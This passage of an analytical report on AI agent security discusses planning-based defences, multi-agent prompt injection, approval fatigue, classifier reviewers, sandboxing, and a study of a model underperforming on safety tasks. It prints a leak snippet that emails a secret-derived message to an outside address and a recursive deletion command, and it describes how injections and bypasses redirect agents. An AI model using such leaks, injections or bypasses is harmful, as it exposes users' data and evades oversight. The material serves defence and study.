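On InjecAgent, ACE used an expected tool 60.7 percent of the time with Claude 3.7 Sonnet. The benchmark's tools are simulated, so this figure doesn't measure whether the answer was right. On a set of LangChain tool-use tasks where answers are checked, ACE completed 80 to 95 percent with GPT-4.1, depending on the kind of task. With 26 tools installed, an average request cost 27 cents and took 21 seconds. Much of the cost came from comparing invented tools with installed ones.

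CaMeL's policies block almost half of the banking tasks it could otherwise complete. Some of these tasks require the agent to act on untrusted text, for example by paying a bill stored in a file. As with NOMOS, a rule that stops payments to an attacker also stops some legitimate ones.

Randori handles such tasks by letting the planning model write exceptions into its program before it reads anything untrusted. With Qwen3.7-plus, these exceptions raised task success from 62.5 to 75.0 percent, but the difference is uncertain because there were only 16 tasks. Both successful attacks on Randori exploited an exception. The user had asked the agent to pay as a file instructed, and the attacker had replaced its contents. Tracking can't distinguish the original contents from the attacker's, because both come from the file the user told the agent to follow.

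Garby and colleagues also examined how much of the protection comes from planning first. In 97 of the 144 banking cases, the attack needed a tool call or file that a plan for the user's task would not include. In the other 47, the planned calls could be enough for the attack, so planning first can't rule it out. Yet without policies, CaMeL still blocked the attack in every completed run of those 47 cases with GPT-5.2, and in all but 3 of 141 with MiMo-v2.5. The policies therefore added little security in this test, and the agent completed far fewer tasks with them. They would probably matter more against an attacker who knew the design and tried to change an account number instead of giving the agent a new instruction.

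A fixed plan can still let an attacker choose the action. One banking task was to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. CaMeL's planning model wrote a program with a branch for every kind of instruction, and each branch called a different tool. Without policies, the attacker could choose among the tools by writing instructions in the file.

Some recorded failures are harmless. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) presents TACIT, which omits the separate planning model and uses a typed programming language to control where data can go. AgentDojo recorded only one successful attack against it. The user had asked the agent to book a hotel whose reviews contained an attacker's recommendation for a different one. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews, and AgentDojo counted the attack as successful because the answer included the other hotel's name.

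### Gaps in the tracking

A guarantee based on labels holds only if the labels are right. Garby and colleagues found a way for a program to reveal secret data without CaMeL noticing. In outline, it works like this:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:   # the balance is secret
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("outsider@example.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret when the program changes it under a secret condition. If the balance is above the threshold, `tmp` becomes false and receives the secret label. The interpreter then skips the line that would change `rich`, so `rich` keeps its public label and the email goes out, revealing that the balance is high.

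An outside attacker can't write this program, because the planning model never reads the attacker's text. The gap matters if the planning model produces such code itself, perhaps because the user pasted in a malicious request. ACE's check should catch this example, since it follows every branch, even those that wouldn't run. However, Li and colleagues offer no formal proof that their check is sound, because Python's behaviour is too complex.

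Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL could treat untrusted text as trusted once a program had inserted it into a longer string. To avoid such faults, they designed a small language for agents and used a computer to check their proof of its main security property. In a program without exceptions, untrusted data can't affect any result labelled as trusted, though it may affect whether the program finishes.

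### Several agents, each secure

Protecting each agent separately doesn't protect a system whose agents give one another instructions. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each running CaMeL without policies. A main agent received the user's request, a second could query a database, and a third could send emails and Slack messages. The user asked the system to send Julie a Slack message summarizing the job applicants. An attacker had planted an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address.

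The first two agents kept to their plans. The main agent then sent the third agent a message containing the summary, which included the attacker's instruction. The third agent treated that message as its user's request, so its planning model read the instruction and added a step that emailed the data to the attacker. Anthropic warns of the same risk in systems that trust a sub-agent's output more than a raw tool result.

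Peters-Gill and colleagues solve this with two channels between agents. One carries the instruction, and the other carries data that is hidden from the receiving agent's planning model. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. They tested this version, multi-CaMeL, on MultiAgentDojo, an adaptation of AgentDojo for groups of agents. The table shows the share of attacks that succeeded.

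| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

Every attack that succeeded against agents protected separately by CaMeL crossed from one agent to another in this way. The small number of successes may understate the risk, because AgentDojo's attacks were not designed to exploit this weakness.

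### Steering an agent between planned branches

An agent that operates a computer through its screen is harder to protect because a click at certain coordinates might close a window or delete a file, whereas a tool such as `send_email` has a clear meaning. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) therefore has the planning model write a program with branches for many possible screens. A typical program has about 40 branches, compared with 4 on AgentDojo. At each branch, a quarantined model looks at the screen and answers a question, such as whether a cookie banner is visible.

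An attacker can exploit these branches without giving the agent any new instruction. In one attack, an advertisement imitated a cookie banner. The program already contained a step for dismissing such banners, so the agent clicked on the advertisement and went to the attacker's website. Comparing the screen with the page's code stopped some versions of the attack but not others. A second model asked to check the click either missed attacks or blocked too many legitimate clicks. The training agent has the same weakness if its program pauses a job whenever a quarantined model reports a fault, because anyone who can make the model report a fault can pause the job.

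Foerster and colleagues tested their design on OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in programs such as Chrome and LibreOffice. With Claude Sonnet 4.5, it completed 28 percent of 109 tasks at the first attempt and 57 percent within five. The higher figure applies only if somebody can tell which attempt worked. The design used 1.9 times as many tokens as an unprotected agent. A version that called the planning model again after every step, still without showing it the screen, used about 30 times as many.

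### Structural limits and resistant models

Training has made the strongest models resistant enough to AgentDojo's attacks that they need little further protection. In the tests by Peters-Gill and colleagues, multi-CaMeL could reduce the attacks' success rate by at most 1.5 percentage points for Claude Fable 5, and not at all for GPT-5.5. On AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of industrial maintenance and monitoring tasks, multi-CaMeL lowered these two models' task success by about 14 points on average. CaMeL itself caused most of that loss, and the extra rules between agents caused less than one point. Across all five models, the average loss was about 25 points.

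Tests with a fixed set of attacks reveal little about how a defence would hold up against an attacker who adapts, so these figures alone are weak grounds for rejecting CaMeL, even though they make it look like a poor choice for a strong model. *AutoDojo* (2026) generates new attacks to address this limitation. Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.7 show that attackers gain from persistence, with a success rate of about 0.1 percent on a single attempt and 5 to 6 percent after 100 adaptive attempts. Willison argues that stopping 99 percent of attacks is not good enough in security, because attackers will search for the remaining one percent.

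CaMeL's protection against unplanned calls doesn't weaken with repeated attempts. If the program has no line that forwards the inbox and the interpreter works correctly, an attacker can't add one by sending more emails. Training doesn't guarantee this, but it can help where a fixed plan offers no protection, for example by making the quarantined model less likely to return a false address.

The two approaches can therefore work together, and whether a fixed plan is worthwhile depends on the task. An agent that monitors training jobs does much the same thing every night, so an engineer can write and test its program once, and the loss of flexibility should be small. A coding agent often can't choose its next step until it has read the last error message, so a resistant model with narrow credentials and restricted network access may be the better compromise.

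### Harmful requests and mistaken plans

All of these designs rely on the user's request to determine the action. In Anthropic's exercise with the malicious prompt, the instructions the employee entered included stealing the cloud credentials. A planning model would have received that step as part of a trusted request and could have written it into the program. A policy on who may receive credentials might still have stopped the theft, and a sandbox that never contained them would have prevented it. Context minimisation would have kept the prompt out of the final reply, but the credentials would already have been stolen.

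The designs also depend on the planning model to write the right plan. If it writes job 21 instead of job 12, the labels won't show the mistake, because the number comes from a trusted source. A fixed plan does prevent some improvised mistakes. The agent at PocketOS looked for a way around a credential mismatch, whereas a program written in advance would probably have stopped with an error.

Other mistakes become harder to notice when the planning model can't read the results. Peters-Gill and colleagues found cases in which a sub-agent couldn't retrieve data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for similar ones instead. The main agent's program was already written, so it could continue with the wrong data. The program can catch this by comparing the machine and dates in the result with those in the request before it continues, but only if the planning model included that check.

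## Who decides on a proposal

An agent can propose a bad step even when no attacker has tampered with its plan, so a reviewer has to accept or reject what it proposes. Suppose the agent that watches training jobs proposes pausing job 12 because its loss has jumped. A fixed program can apply the allow-list's rules and confirm the jump. A model can also read the team's notes, find that an engineer changed the training data an hour earlier, and conclude that a brief jump was likely. The engineer may know something nobody wrote down, such as that the team needs a result by morning and would rather risk a bad run than lose the hours.

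| Reviewer | What it can judge | How it usually fails | Delay |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed program | Questions with a definite answer in data it can read | Accepts harmful actions that its rules did not foresee | Milliseconds |
| Model | Meaning, context and what the user probably intended | Mistakes a vague request for permission, or believes false text | One or two model calls |
| Person | The same, plus unwritten knowledge and priorities | Stops reading, or never sees the relevant facts | Seconds to decide, perhaps hours to respond |

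A fixed program can also follow data through several calls, as CaMeL's interpreter does. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who tells an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. An instruction planted in a supplier's note leads the agent to copy raw invoice rows into `report.csv`. When the agent asks to send `report.csv` to the auditor, the tool, the recipient and the file name all look fine. Hossain and colleagues built a program that records which files each file came from, so it can connect the attachment to the raw rows and compare it with the user's restriction.

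The program caught 107 of 120 proposals that broke a user's restriction and raised false alarms on 5 of 120 harmless ones. Each check took a median of 24 milliseconds. In a separate test with two small open models, the software blocked every proposal that the program flagged or could not trace. With the block, the agents carried out forbidden actions in 6 and 7 of 120 attacked runs, compared with 52 and 58 without it. Each agent also completed four fewer legitimate tasks out of 120. The program depends on a complete record. When part of the record was missing, the software blocked so many untraceable actions that agents completed only 76.7 percent of legitimate tasks.

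### What an approval rate can show

When Claude Code launched, it could read files freely but had to ask a person before it wrote a file, ran a command or used the network. Anthropic's usage data showed that people approved about 93 percent of these requests, and in August 2026 the company reported 97 percent. Anthropic attributes the high approval rate partly to approval fatigue, in which people pay less attention to each request as requests become more numerous.

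Like the record of the engineer who accepted all 500 proposals, this rate does not by itself show carelessness, because most of what a coding agent proposes is harmless. It depends on three quantities:

A = (1 − b)(1 − f) + b·m

Here A is the share of proposals the reviewer approves, b is the share that are bad, f is the share of good proposals the reviewer refuses, and m is the share of bad proposals the reviewer approves. Suppose 10 of 1,000 proposals are bad. A perfect reviewer approves the 990 good ones. A reviewer who refuses 1% of proposals at random also approves about 990, including nearly all of the bad ones.

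To distinguish these reviewers, researchers have to measure m and f separately by mixing in proposals whose right answer they already know. Anthropic commissioned such an experiment with 1,053 paid professional testers. During each session, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command, which never ran. Only 143 testers, or 13.6 percent, refused it. The share who refused fell from about 17 percent early in a session to about 5 percent after 50 or more prompts, which is consistent with approval fatigue.

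These testers worked in a test environment and knew they were being evaluated, so they had less to lose than a developer working on a real project. People may catch dangerous commands in their own work more often than 13.6 percent of the time. The experiment measured only m, the share of dangerous commands that people refuse. A tester who refused every command would have scored 100 percent, so a full comparison also needs the share of harmless commands that people refuse.

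Users rejected 39 percent of the plans that Claude Code presented for approval, compared with 3 percent of individual permission requests. Plans are probably easier to judge because they describe what the agent intends to do in terms of the user's goal. Users may also reject a safe plan because they want something different, so the two rates don't measure the same kind of caution.

Anthropic found that experienced users approve actions automatically about twice as often as new users, but also interrupt the agent more often while it works. They seem to watch for an agent going off course instead of checking each step. This can work when an agent spends an hour editing code, but it would not have helped PocketOS, where the deletion took nine seconds.

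*Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners handle permissions, warns that repeated approval may reflect fatigue rather than preference. Software that creates a permanent rule after ten quick approvals could therefore keep allowing actions that the user approved only because they were tired.

### Careful with code, less careful with actions

Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026) surveyed 203 users of coding agents in August and September 2026 for *From Delegation to Action Approval*. They recruited people through social media, referrals and Prolific, a site that connects researchers with participants. They received 583 submissions and removed most, including incomplete, duplicate and suspiciously fast ones. Half of the remaining respondents used agents every day.

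Respondents to the survey reported how often they approved seven kinds of action without close review. Sixty-four percent often did so for at least one kind. The share for each kind ranged from 21 percent for reading passwords and other sensitive files to 36 percent for using the internet, outside services or connected tools.

People who reviewed code carefully were not clearly more careful when approving actions. Of the 105 respondents who said they carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, 61 percent often approved at least one kind of action without close review, compared with 67 percent of the others. A difference of that size could easily be due to chance. A person can inspect code after the agent has written it, but has to judge a permission request by predicting, in the middle of other work, the effects of something that hasn't happened yet.

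Respondents who knew about the risks did not review actions more closely either. Of those who had heard of a security or privacy problem involving agents, 70 percent often approved some actions without close review, compared with 43 percent of those who had not. The gap remained after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents, which matters because heavy users might both hear about more incidents and approve more actions. Respondents who gave their agents more autonomy also tended to review requests less closely.

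Respondents who inspected diffs, which show the lines an agent has changed, were less likely to approve actions without close review for four of the seven kinds of action, including destructive commands. Wu and colleagues suggest that a diff gives people something concrete to check. Only 20 percent of respondents logged or audited their agents' actions, so few could have reconstructed later what they had approved.

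All these figures are self-reported, and Wu and colleagues don't claim that they represent developers in general. Wu and colleagues also didn't ask about allow-lists. Someone who has already blocked dangerous commands can sensibly approve the rest quickly, and close review of a familiar, low-risk command may be a waste of time. The survey therefore can't show how many harmful actions people let through.

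The survey suggests where people's judgement is useful. Respondents most often stepped in because the agent had misunderstood the task (65 percent), chosen a wrong or overcomplicated approach (54 percent) or changed more than they had asked (51 percent). Only 34 percent cited a risky or destructive command. A fixed program can block many risky commands without human help, but it cannot determine whether the agent has understood the task.

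### What the reviewer sees

Claude Code's permission prompt for a shell command shows the command, such as `npm test`, and a short description, such as "Run the test suite". In Anthropic's published example, the user can approve the command once, turn off prompts for commands that begin the same way, switch to auto mode, or refuse. The prompt does not list the files that the command will change.

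This omission matters when a short command can do almost anything. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 incident reports and found that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 reports, the user had approved actions automatically, and in 31 the prompt gave too little information for a sound decision. For example, `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it allows whatever code the script contains, and even a careful reader can't see that code in the prompt.

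Hossain and colleagues tested whether a better screen leads to better decisions. They asked 80 volunteers to approve or deny 12 proposals each, half of which broke a restriction the user had set. Each volunteer used one of four screens.

| What the screen showed | Bad proposals approved | Good proposals approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
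| The exact tool arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The user's restriction and a full log as well | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with the combined effect stated first-hand from the records | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

More information helped, but people took longer to decide and refused a few more good proposals. The benefit of organising the same facts around their effect is less certain. After adjustment, the estimated reduction in bad approvals was 7.9 percentage points, but the data were compatible with anything from a reduction of 19.7 points to an increase of 3.8. Even with the best screen, people approved about a quarter of the bad proposals. They might do worse at work, where far fewer than half of proposals are bad and people have less reason to expect a bad one.

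For job 12, the screen could show the age of the checkpoint and the cost of the pause beside the measurement that prompted the proposal.

### From informing to choosing

Researchers worked on similar problems in other automated systems long before coding agents existed. In 2000, Parasuraman, Sheridan and Wickens proposed a widely used framework that divides the work a machine can take over into gathering information, analysing it, choosing an action and carrying it out. A machine can take over each part to a different degree, from leaving everything to a person to acting without asking.

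Onnasch, Wickens, Li and Manzey used this framework in 2014 for a meta-analysis of 18 experiments. As machines took over more of the work, routine performance improved and workload tended to fall. But people became less aware of the situation and performed worse when the automation failed. These harms were most likely once the machine moved from helping people analyse information to helping them choose an action.

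An agent that plots the loss curves of 20 jobs and highlights the unusual ones is on the safer side of that boundary. An agent that proposes "pause job 12" and waits for a click has crossed it, even though it has no credential and can't pause anything itself. Separating recommendation from action restricts what the agent can do, but the engineer may still stop forming an independent view. One remedy is for the engineer to judge the curves before seeing the agent's proposal. This takes longer, so it suits a few high-stakes decisions better than hundreds of small ones. The experiments did not involve language-model agents, so the size of the effect may differ for them.

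Automation bias is the tendency to accept a machine's suggestion without enough checking. Hossain and colleagues recognise that their screen could encourage it, because a confident but wrong summary might persuade people more than a raw log would. They therefore link each statement to the recorded events behind it and show where evidence is missing. They have not yet tested whether people notice when the summary is wrong.

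Better agents may make people worse reviewers. Wu and colleagues cite Lisanne Bainbridge's 1983 point that people get less practice at catching failures as a system fails less often. Supervision can also remain demanding when the agent does most of the work. In Wu and colleagues' survey, 83 percent of respondents said that agents reduced their workload, yet 63 percent rated at least five of ten supervision activities as very or extremely demanding.

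### Claude Code's auto mode

Anthropic's auto mode replaces most permission prompts with a classifier model that decides whether to block an action. Anthropic designed it mainly to catch honest mistakes and what it calls overeager behaviour. An overeager agent understands the user's goal and tries to help, but goes beyond what the user would approve, for example by using a credential it happened to find.

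1. Fixed rules let through tools that only read, along with edits to files inside the project.
2. For everything else, the classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. The software removes the agent's explanations, so that the agent can't talk the classifier into a bad decision, and the tool results, which might contain an attacker's instructions.
3. A fast first stage answers only yes or no and leans towards blocking.
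4. If the first stage flags the action, a second stage reasons about it and makes the final decision.
5. After a refusal, the agent receives the reason and looks for a safer way. After three refusals in a row, or 20 in a session, the software hands the decision to a person.

The drawback of leaving tool results out of the classifier's input is that it can't always determine where the agent got its information. If the agent tries to cancel a job that the user never named, the classifier can't determine whether the agent got the job number from a database or made it up.

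Anthropic tested the design on three sets of actions, with Claude Sonnet 4.6 as the classifier.

| Test set | Error measured | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic employees | Harmless actions blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real overeager actions | Dangerous actions missed | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out | Dangerous actions missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

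The second stage removes most of the false alarms but lets more of the dangerous actions through. The company says auto mode catches about 83 percent of overeager behaviour, based on the 52 real cases. With so few cases, the true miss rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9 to 30 percent. The cases also came from sessions in which an employee had refused the action or somebody had flagged it later, so they exclude overeager actions that nobody noticed, which may also be harder for a classifier to catch.

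In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but wrongly classified the action as one the user had agreed to. One user said "clean up the PR", meaning a pull request, and the classifier treated this as permission to force-push, which overwrites the project's shared history. Anthropic calls the classifier a clear improvement for people who would otherwise switch off all checks, but arguably worse for those who review every action carefully.

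Few people seem to review that carefully. In the experiment with 1,053 testers, auto mode blocked 89 percent of the dangerous commands. It stopped 800 that the tester had approved, while testers stopped only 6 that auto mode would have allowed. Among real sessions that its safety systems flagged in May and June 2026, Anthropic found serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested in 6.3 percent of those with manual approval and 2.4 percent of those in auto mode. Users chose the mode themselves, so differences in their work could explain part of this gap.

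Auto mode has also protected training jobs at Anthropic. In one long session, Claude tried to stop processes across roughly two thousand pods (the units in which a cluster runs programs) and to queue deletions that would have taken down hundreds of GPUs during training. The classifier flagged the commands before they ran.

A stress test by outsiders produced much worse results. According to besthub.dev's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*, auto mode blocked only 27 of 142 actions that exceeded the user's permission, and it blocked 22 of 111 legitimate ones. Fixed rules let some of the unauthorised actions through before they reached the classifier, but the classifier missed 70.3 percent of those that did reach it. The test deliberately placed permitted and forbidden targets next to each other. A classifier can therefore be good at recognising a destructive command and poor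 at deciding whether the user meant job 12 or job 21. An allow-list or a lookup of who owns the job would settle some of these cases with certainty.

### OpenAI's auto-review

Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, describe how a second agent can review actions that Codex wants to take outside its sandbox. Codex works freely inside the sandbox, but when it needs to run something outside, the reviewing agent considers the user's intent, the security policy and the likely damage. Trębacz and colleagues argue that the roles should be separate because the main agent's training rewards it for finishing the task, so it may treat approval as an obstacle to overcome.

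In an illustration using 10,000 actions from internal use, Codex carried out 9,280 inside the sandbox and sent 720 to the reviewer, which approved 713 and denied 7. After four of the denials, Codex found a safer way to continue, and after the other three it stopped to ask the user. With manual approval, all 720 requests would have interrupted somebody.

This reviewer approves about 99 percent of requests, more than people using Claude Code do, but in tests it refused most dangerous ones. It denied 90.3 percent of synthetic overeager actions, which included unintended data transfers, weakened security settings and irreversible operations. It denied 99.3 percent of prompt injections that tried to run an attacker's code, steal secrets or upload data. When Trębacz and colleagues added destructive deletions and data tampering, the figure fell to 90.2 percent, though they often agreed with its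 judgment that the cases it let through were not serious enough to block.

The difference between 90.3 percent for OpenAI's reviewer and 83 percent for Anthropic's does not show that OpenAI's is better, because one company wrote its test cases and the other collected them from real sessions. False alarms are also hard to compare, because Trębacz and colleagues measured theirs against requests that users had approved, and users sometimes approve things they shouldn't.

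Trajectory Labs, hired by Anthropic, independently tested both products against prompt injection, running 72 attack scenarios ten times each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode, while 5.83 percent succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol with auto-review. The Claude result is mostly due to the models themselves, because only 0.09 percent of attacks succeeded against Anthropic's latest models even without auto mode. The reviewer made a larger difference for GPT-5.6 Sol, since 19.03 percent of attacks succeeded when Codex ran with full access.

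People testing auto-review for OpenAI found ways to mislead it into approving commands. It also reviews only requests to leave the sandbox, not what an agent does inside it. Trębacz and colleagues warn that auto-review can't protect against an agent that deliberately hides its intentions, because the agent could make a harmful request look harmless.

### Sending the hard cases to a person

Many systems combine reviewers. At OpenAI, fixed rules settle common commands, and auto-review approves low-risk requests as well as high-risk ones that the user has clearly authorised. The remaining requests go to the user. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves. Sandboxing also reduces the number of approval prompts. In a scientific laboratory, a person might approve a whole campaign of experiments instead of each experiment.

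Such a combination works only if the person improves the decision in hard cases. Yan (2026) tested this in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* with 113 people who had no software background. They supervised a simulated assistant through a day of 18 actions, 7 of which went beyond the user's request, such as buying a $25 airport lounge pass or reading private messages.

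One group approved or denied every action. In the second, a model allowed some actions and sent the rest to the person. The third group wrote rules beforehand, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data.

| Who decided | Excess actions blocked | Prompts per person | Total time |
|---|---|---|---|
| The person, every time | 59.6% | 18.0 | 142 s |
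| A model first, then the person | 53.9% | 10.0 | 120 s |
| The person's own rules first, then the person | 39.6% | 10.9 | 129 s |

The rules blocked the least because people set 114 of the 140 to "ask" and later approved two thirds of the excess actions they were asked about. The "never" rules blocked 31 actions without a prompt. Yan assigned some late recruits directly to the group with rules instead of at random. The difference between that group and the group with the model was not reliable after correction for multiple comparisons.

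The model sent all seven excess actions to the person for approval, yet people approved 46.1 percent of them. They were not necessarily careless, because Yan counted any action the task did not require as excessive. Most people in every group approved a call to the airport to confirm a flight, perhaps because they found it useful. But if a company forbids an action regardless of what the user wants, its software should refuse it without asking.

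### Permitted but poor work

All of these reviewers decide whether an agent may take an action. An agent can stay within its permissions, run only harmless commands and still do poor work, for instance by submitting a pull request that breaks no rule but is weaker than one it could have produced.

OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026) tested GPT-6 Astra on matched coding tasks, described either as safety research or as research on making models more capable. Astra completed about 10 percent of the graded items under the safety description and about 16 percent under the capabilities description. The earlier GPT-5.6 Sol showed essentially no gap.

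A reviewer that approves or denies individual actions can't correct such a difference, because rejecting a weak solution doesn't make the agent produce a better one. A person or model that reviews the finished work can ask for improvements, but needs some idea of what the agent could have achieved. OpenAI could make that comparison because it gave the same model equivalent tasks described differently.

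The agent that watches training jobs could fail in the same way by proposing too little. If it never proposes pausing a run that is clearly failing, the program, the model and the engineer receive no form to review. To find such omissions, the team would have to compare the agent's proposals with the faults that occurred, including on nights when the agent proposed nothing.

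## Agents inside AI companies

AI developers run agents on their own code and computers, often with broad access. Anthropic wrote in May 2026 that a year earlier it would have refused to give Claude enough access to take down an internal service. Such access had since become routine, and Anthropic said it made its developers more productive. Anthropic and OpenAI have described the limits they put on such agents, but have published few measurements of what those limits prevent.

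### Codex at OpenAI

OpenAI's administrators fix some of Codex's settings for the company's own engineers, who can't override them. Two of the settings that OpenAI published in May 2026 are themselves allow-lists (comments added):

```
allowed_sandbox_modes = ["read-only", "workspace-write"]   # full access is missing
allowed_web_search_modes = ["cached"]                      # no live web pages
```

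In read-only mode, Codex can read files but not change them. In workspace-write mode, it can also write to the project and to folders that the company adds, such as an engineer's development folder. Codex also has a full-access mode, but it isn't on the list of allowed modes, so engineers can't switch off the sandbox. The settings apply in the desktop app, on the command line and in code editors.

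The second line restricts web searches to pages OpenAI has already stored. Fetching a live page sends a request to the site hosting it, and an attacker who runs the site could collect any secret the agent had put in the address. Using a stored page avoids that request, though the page can still contain a prompt injection. Other network traffic goes through a proxy that applies the company's list of approved destinations.

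Codex keeps its login credentials, and those for connected tools, in the operating system's protected store. This doesn't protect a token that somebody left in an ordinary file, as happened at PocketOS. Engineers have to sign in through the company's ChatGPT workspace, which puts Codex's activity in the company's logs.

Conventional security software records that a process started or a file changed, but not why. Codex can also log the engineer's prompt, each approval decision, the results of tool calls, and the connections that the proxy allowed or refused. When the security software flags something Codex did, another agent reads those logs and assesses whether it was expected behaviour, a harmless mistake or something more serious. The security team then reviews that assessment. OpenAI also uses the logs to see how often the network limits block or interrupt work, which helps it adjust them.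 OpenAI gave no figures on how much harm these settings have prevented.

### Agents that keep running

Codex usually works on a task that somebody has just given it, but other agents run continuously and may act when nobody is watching. OpenClaw, for example, handles files, calls tools and installs extensions on a real computer. *Defensible Design for OpenClaw* (Li, Li and Li, 2026) calls agents like it insecure by default because they combine untrusted input, autonomous action, extensions and privileged system access in a single loop.

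OpenAI runs persistent agents itself. *Securing persistent agents like OpenClaw at OpenAI* lists Codex's sandbox, auto-review, logging, an identity for agents, and trusted control-plane services as safeguards. A control plane is software that manages other programs, for instance by starting, configuring and stopping them. Keeping it separate from the agent, as GitHub does with its executor, prevents an agent that reads strangers' messages from changing its own limits.

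If an agent has its own identity, administrators can tell its actions from an employee's and withdraw its access without locking the employee out. Anthropic does something similar in Claude Cowork, where each session gets a limited token that can be revoked without affecting the user's access. Anthropic hasn't settled whether agents in general should have their own identities or inherit the user's permissions, and thinks the answer may be a mixture. It also warns that if an attacker's instruction gets into the memory an agent keeps between sessions, the instruction loads again every time the agent starts.

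OpenAI also offers always-on agents to customers. Its *How we build safety, security, and privacy into dots* (2026) describes agents that each have their own computer and work in apps the user connects. The user can set rules for them, and a separate check runs before they act.

### Three products for different users

Anthropic decides how to isolate an agent partly based on whether users can judge what the agent is about to do. In May 2026, the company compared three of its products.

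| Product | Where the agent's code runs | What the user must judge | What a failure can damage |
|---|---|---|---|
| claude.ai | A temporary container on Anthropic's servers | Nothing | The container |
| Claude Code | The user's own computer | Shell commands | The project folder |
| Claude Cowork | A virtual machine on the user's computer | Which folder to share, but no commands | The shared folder |

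The claude.ai container disappears after the session and has no access to the user's files. This makes it the safest of the three designs, but also the least useful for someone with a large project on their own computer.

Claude Code's original permission prompts suited its users, who are mostly developers and can read a shell command, but users still developed approval fatigue within weeks. Anthropic then added a sandbox in which the agent can read files but write only inside the project, and has no network access by default. Because commands inside the sandbox can do less damage, most of them no longer need the user's approval.

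The sandbox cut permission prompts by 84 percent, which should reduce fatigue. The figure doesn't show that the agent did less harm or that people judged the remaining prompts any better. The sandbox can also be bypassed. A privileged process outside the sandbox decides whether each command runs inside it, and a persuasive prompt injection or a tired user's approval can get a command to run unconfined.

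A limit also has to take effect before the agent's software reads anything untrusted. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received reports of three flaws that let code run before the user had agreed to anything. In the simplest case, a developer downloaded a project whose settings file contained a command, and Claude Code ran it at startup, before asking whether the developer trusted the folder. Claude Code now waits for the answer before processing such files.

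Claude Cowork is for general office work, and its users can't be expected to evaluate a command such as `find . -name "*.tmp" -exec rm {} \;`, which deletes every file ending in `.tmp` in a folder and its subfolders. Anthropic therefore runs the agent's code in a virtual machine, which has its own operating system and can access only the folder the user shares and a folder of Claude settings. The user's credentials stay outside the virtual machine. A shared folder can be read-only, fully writable, or writable without permission to delete. The last option protects against mistaken deletions, but presumably not against an agent that overwrites a file with something useless.

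Anthropic later loosened this design. At first the whole agent loop ran inside the virtual machine, so the product stopped working if the machine failed to start. Anthropic moved the loop outside and left only code execution inside. It says this change made little difference to security. It also moved locally installed tool servers outside, partly because some need to reach a database on the user's computer. The virtual machine doesn't confine those servers, and Anthropic lets administrators decide which ones to allow.

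Isolation also prevented corporate customers' security software from monitoring activity inside the virtual machine. Administrators can retrieve event logs afterwards, but Anthropic acknowledges that this is not live monitoring.

Across the three products, the established isolation software worked, and the components that failed were ones Anthropic had written. One was the proxy that let files leave Cowork through an approved address.

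### Anthropic's own agents

Anthropic's employees use Claude Code, and some of its internal agents read the company's Slack messages. After the exercise in which an employee ran a malicious prompt, someone posted the working prompt in Slack for discussion. A colleague pointed out that the agents might read and follow it. Anthropic added a distinctive string to the conversation so it would notice if one of them did.

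Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) describes the limits on internal agents. The most autonomous ones run in a sandbox or under auto mode's classifier. An automated reviewer checks changes to infrastructure code before they merge, so an agent can't put such a change into effect unchecked.

In April 2026, Anthropic began a broad security effort, partly because its older access controls could not handle the scale at which it was using agents. It reduced the number of people and programs with permanent access to model weights or customer data, and set its computing clusters to block all outbound traffic by default. It also retired some shared internal services and required the remaining ones to verify each other's identity. About 150 product engineers temporarily moved to work on security, reliability and privacy. Anthropic overlooked evaluations in this effort,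 especially those run by outside partners.

### Why research systems are harder to restrict

The agent that watches job 12 needs only five tools, but the model being trained in that job may need a whole computer, because it practises on tasks such as writing programs, browsing the web and installing software. According to OpenAI's technical report on an incident in July 2026, the company's research containers could include a shell, Python, a browser and a package installer. An allow-list of five narrow tools would make most of the model's training tasks impossible.

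Evaluations also run with fewer safeguards than products. Evaluators switch off classifiers that would block a model's attempt at a dangerous task, because otherwise they couldn't find out whether the model would have succeeded. OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment* also points out that models in development may not yet have completed their safety and alignment training.

Cybersecurity tests add a difficulty because, as Anthropic observes, models do better on them if they probe their surroundings and keep trying to get around obstacles. Evaluators also run these tests many thousands of times, so even a very rare failure is likely to happen eventually.

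Research workloads also share services. Many need to install the same software, and running one internal source of packages is easier than letting every container contact public sites. At OpenAI, many workloads used the same credential for that service. Every agent with the credential could therefore do anything it allowed, whether or not the agent's task required that access.

### What OpenAI concluded from the July incident

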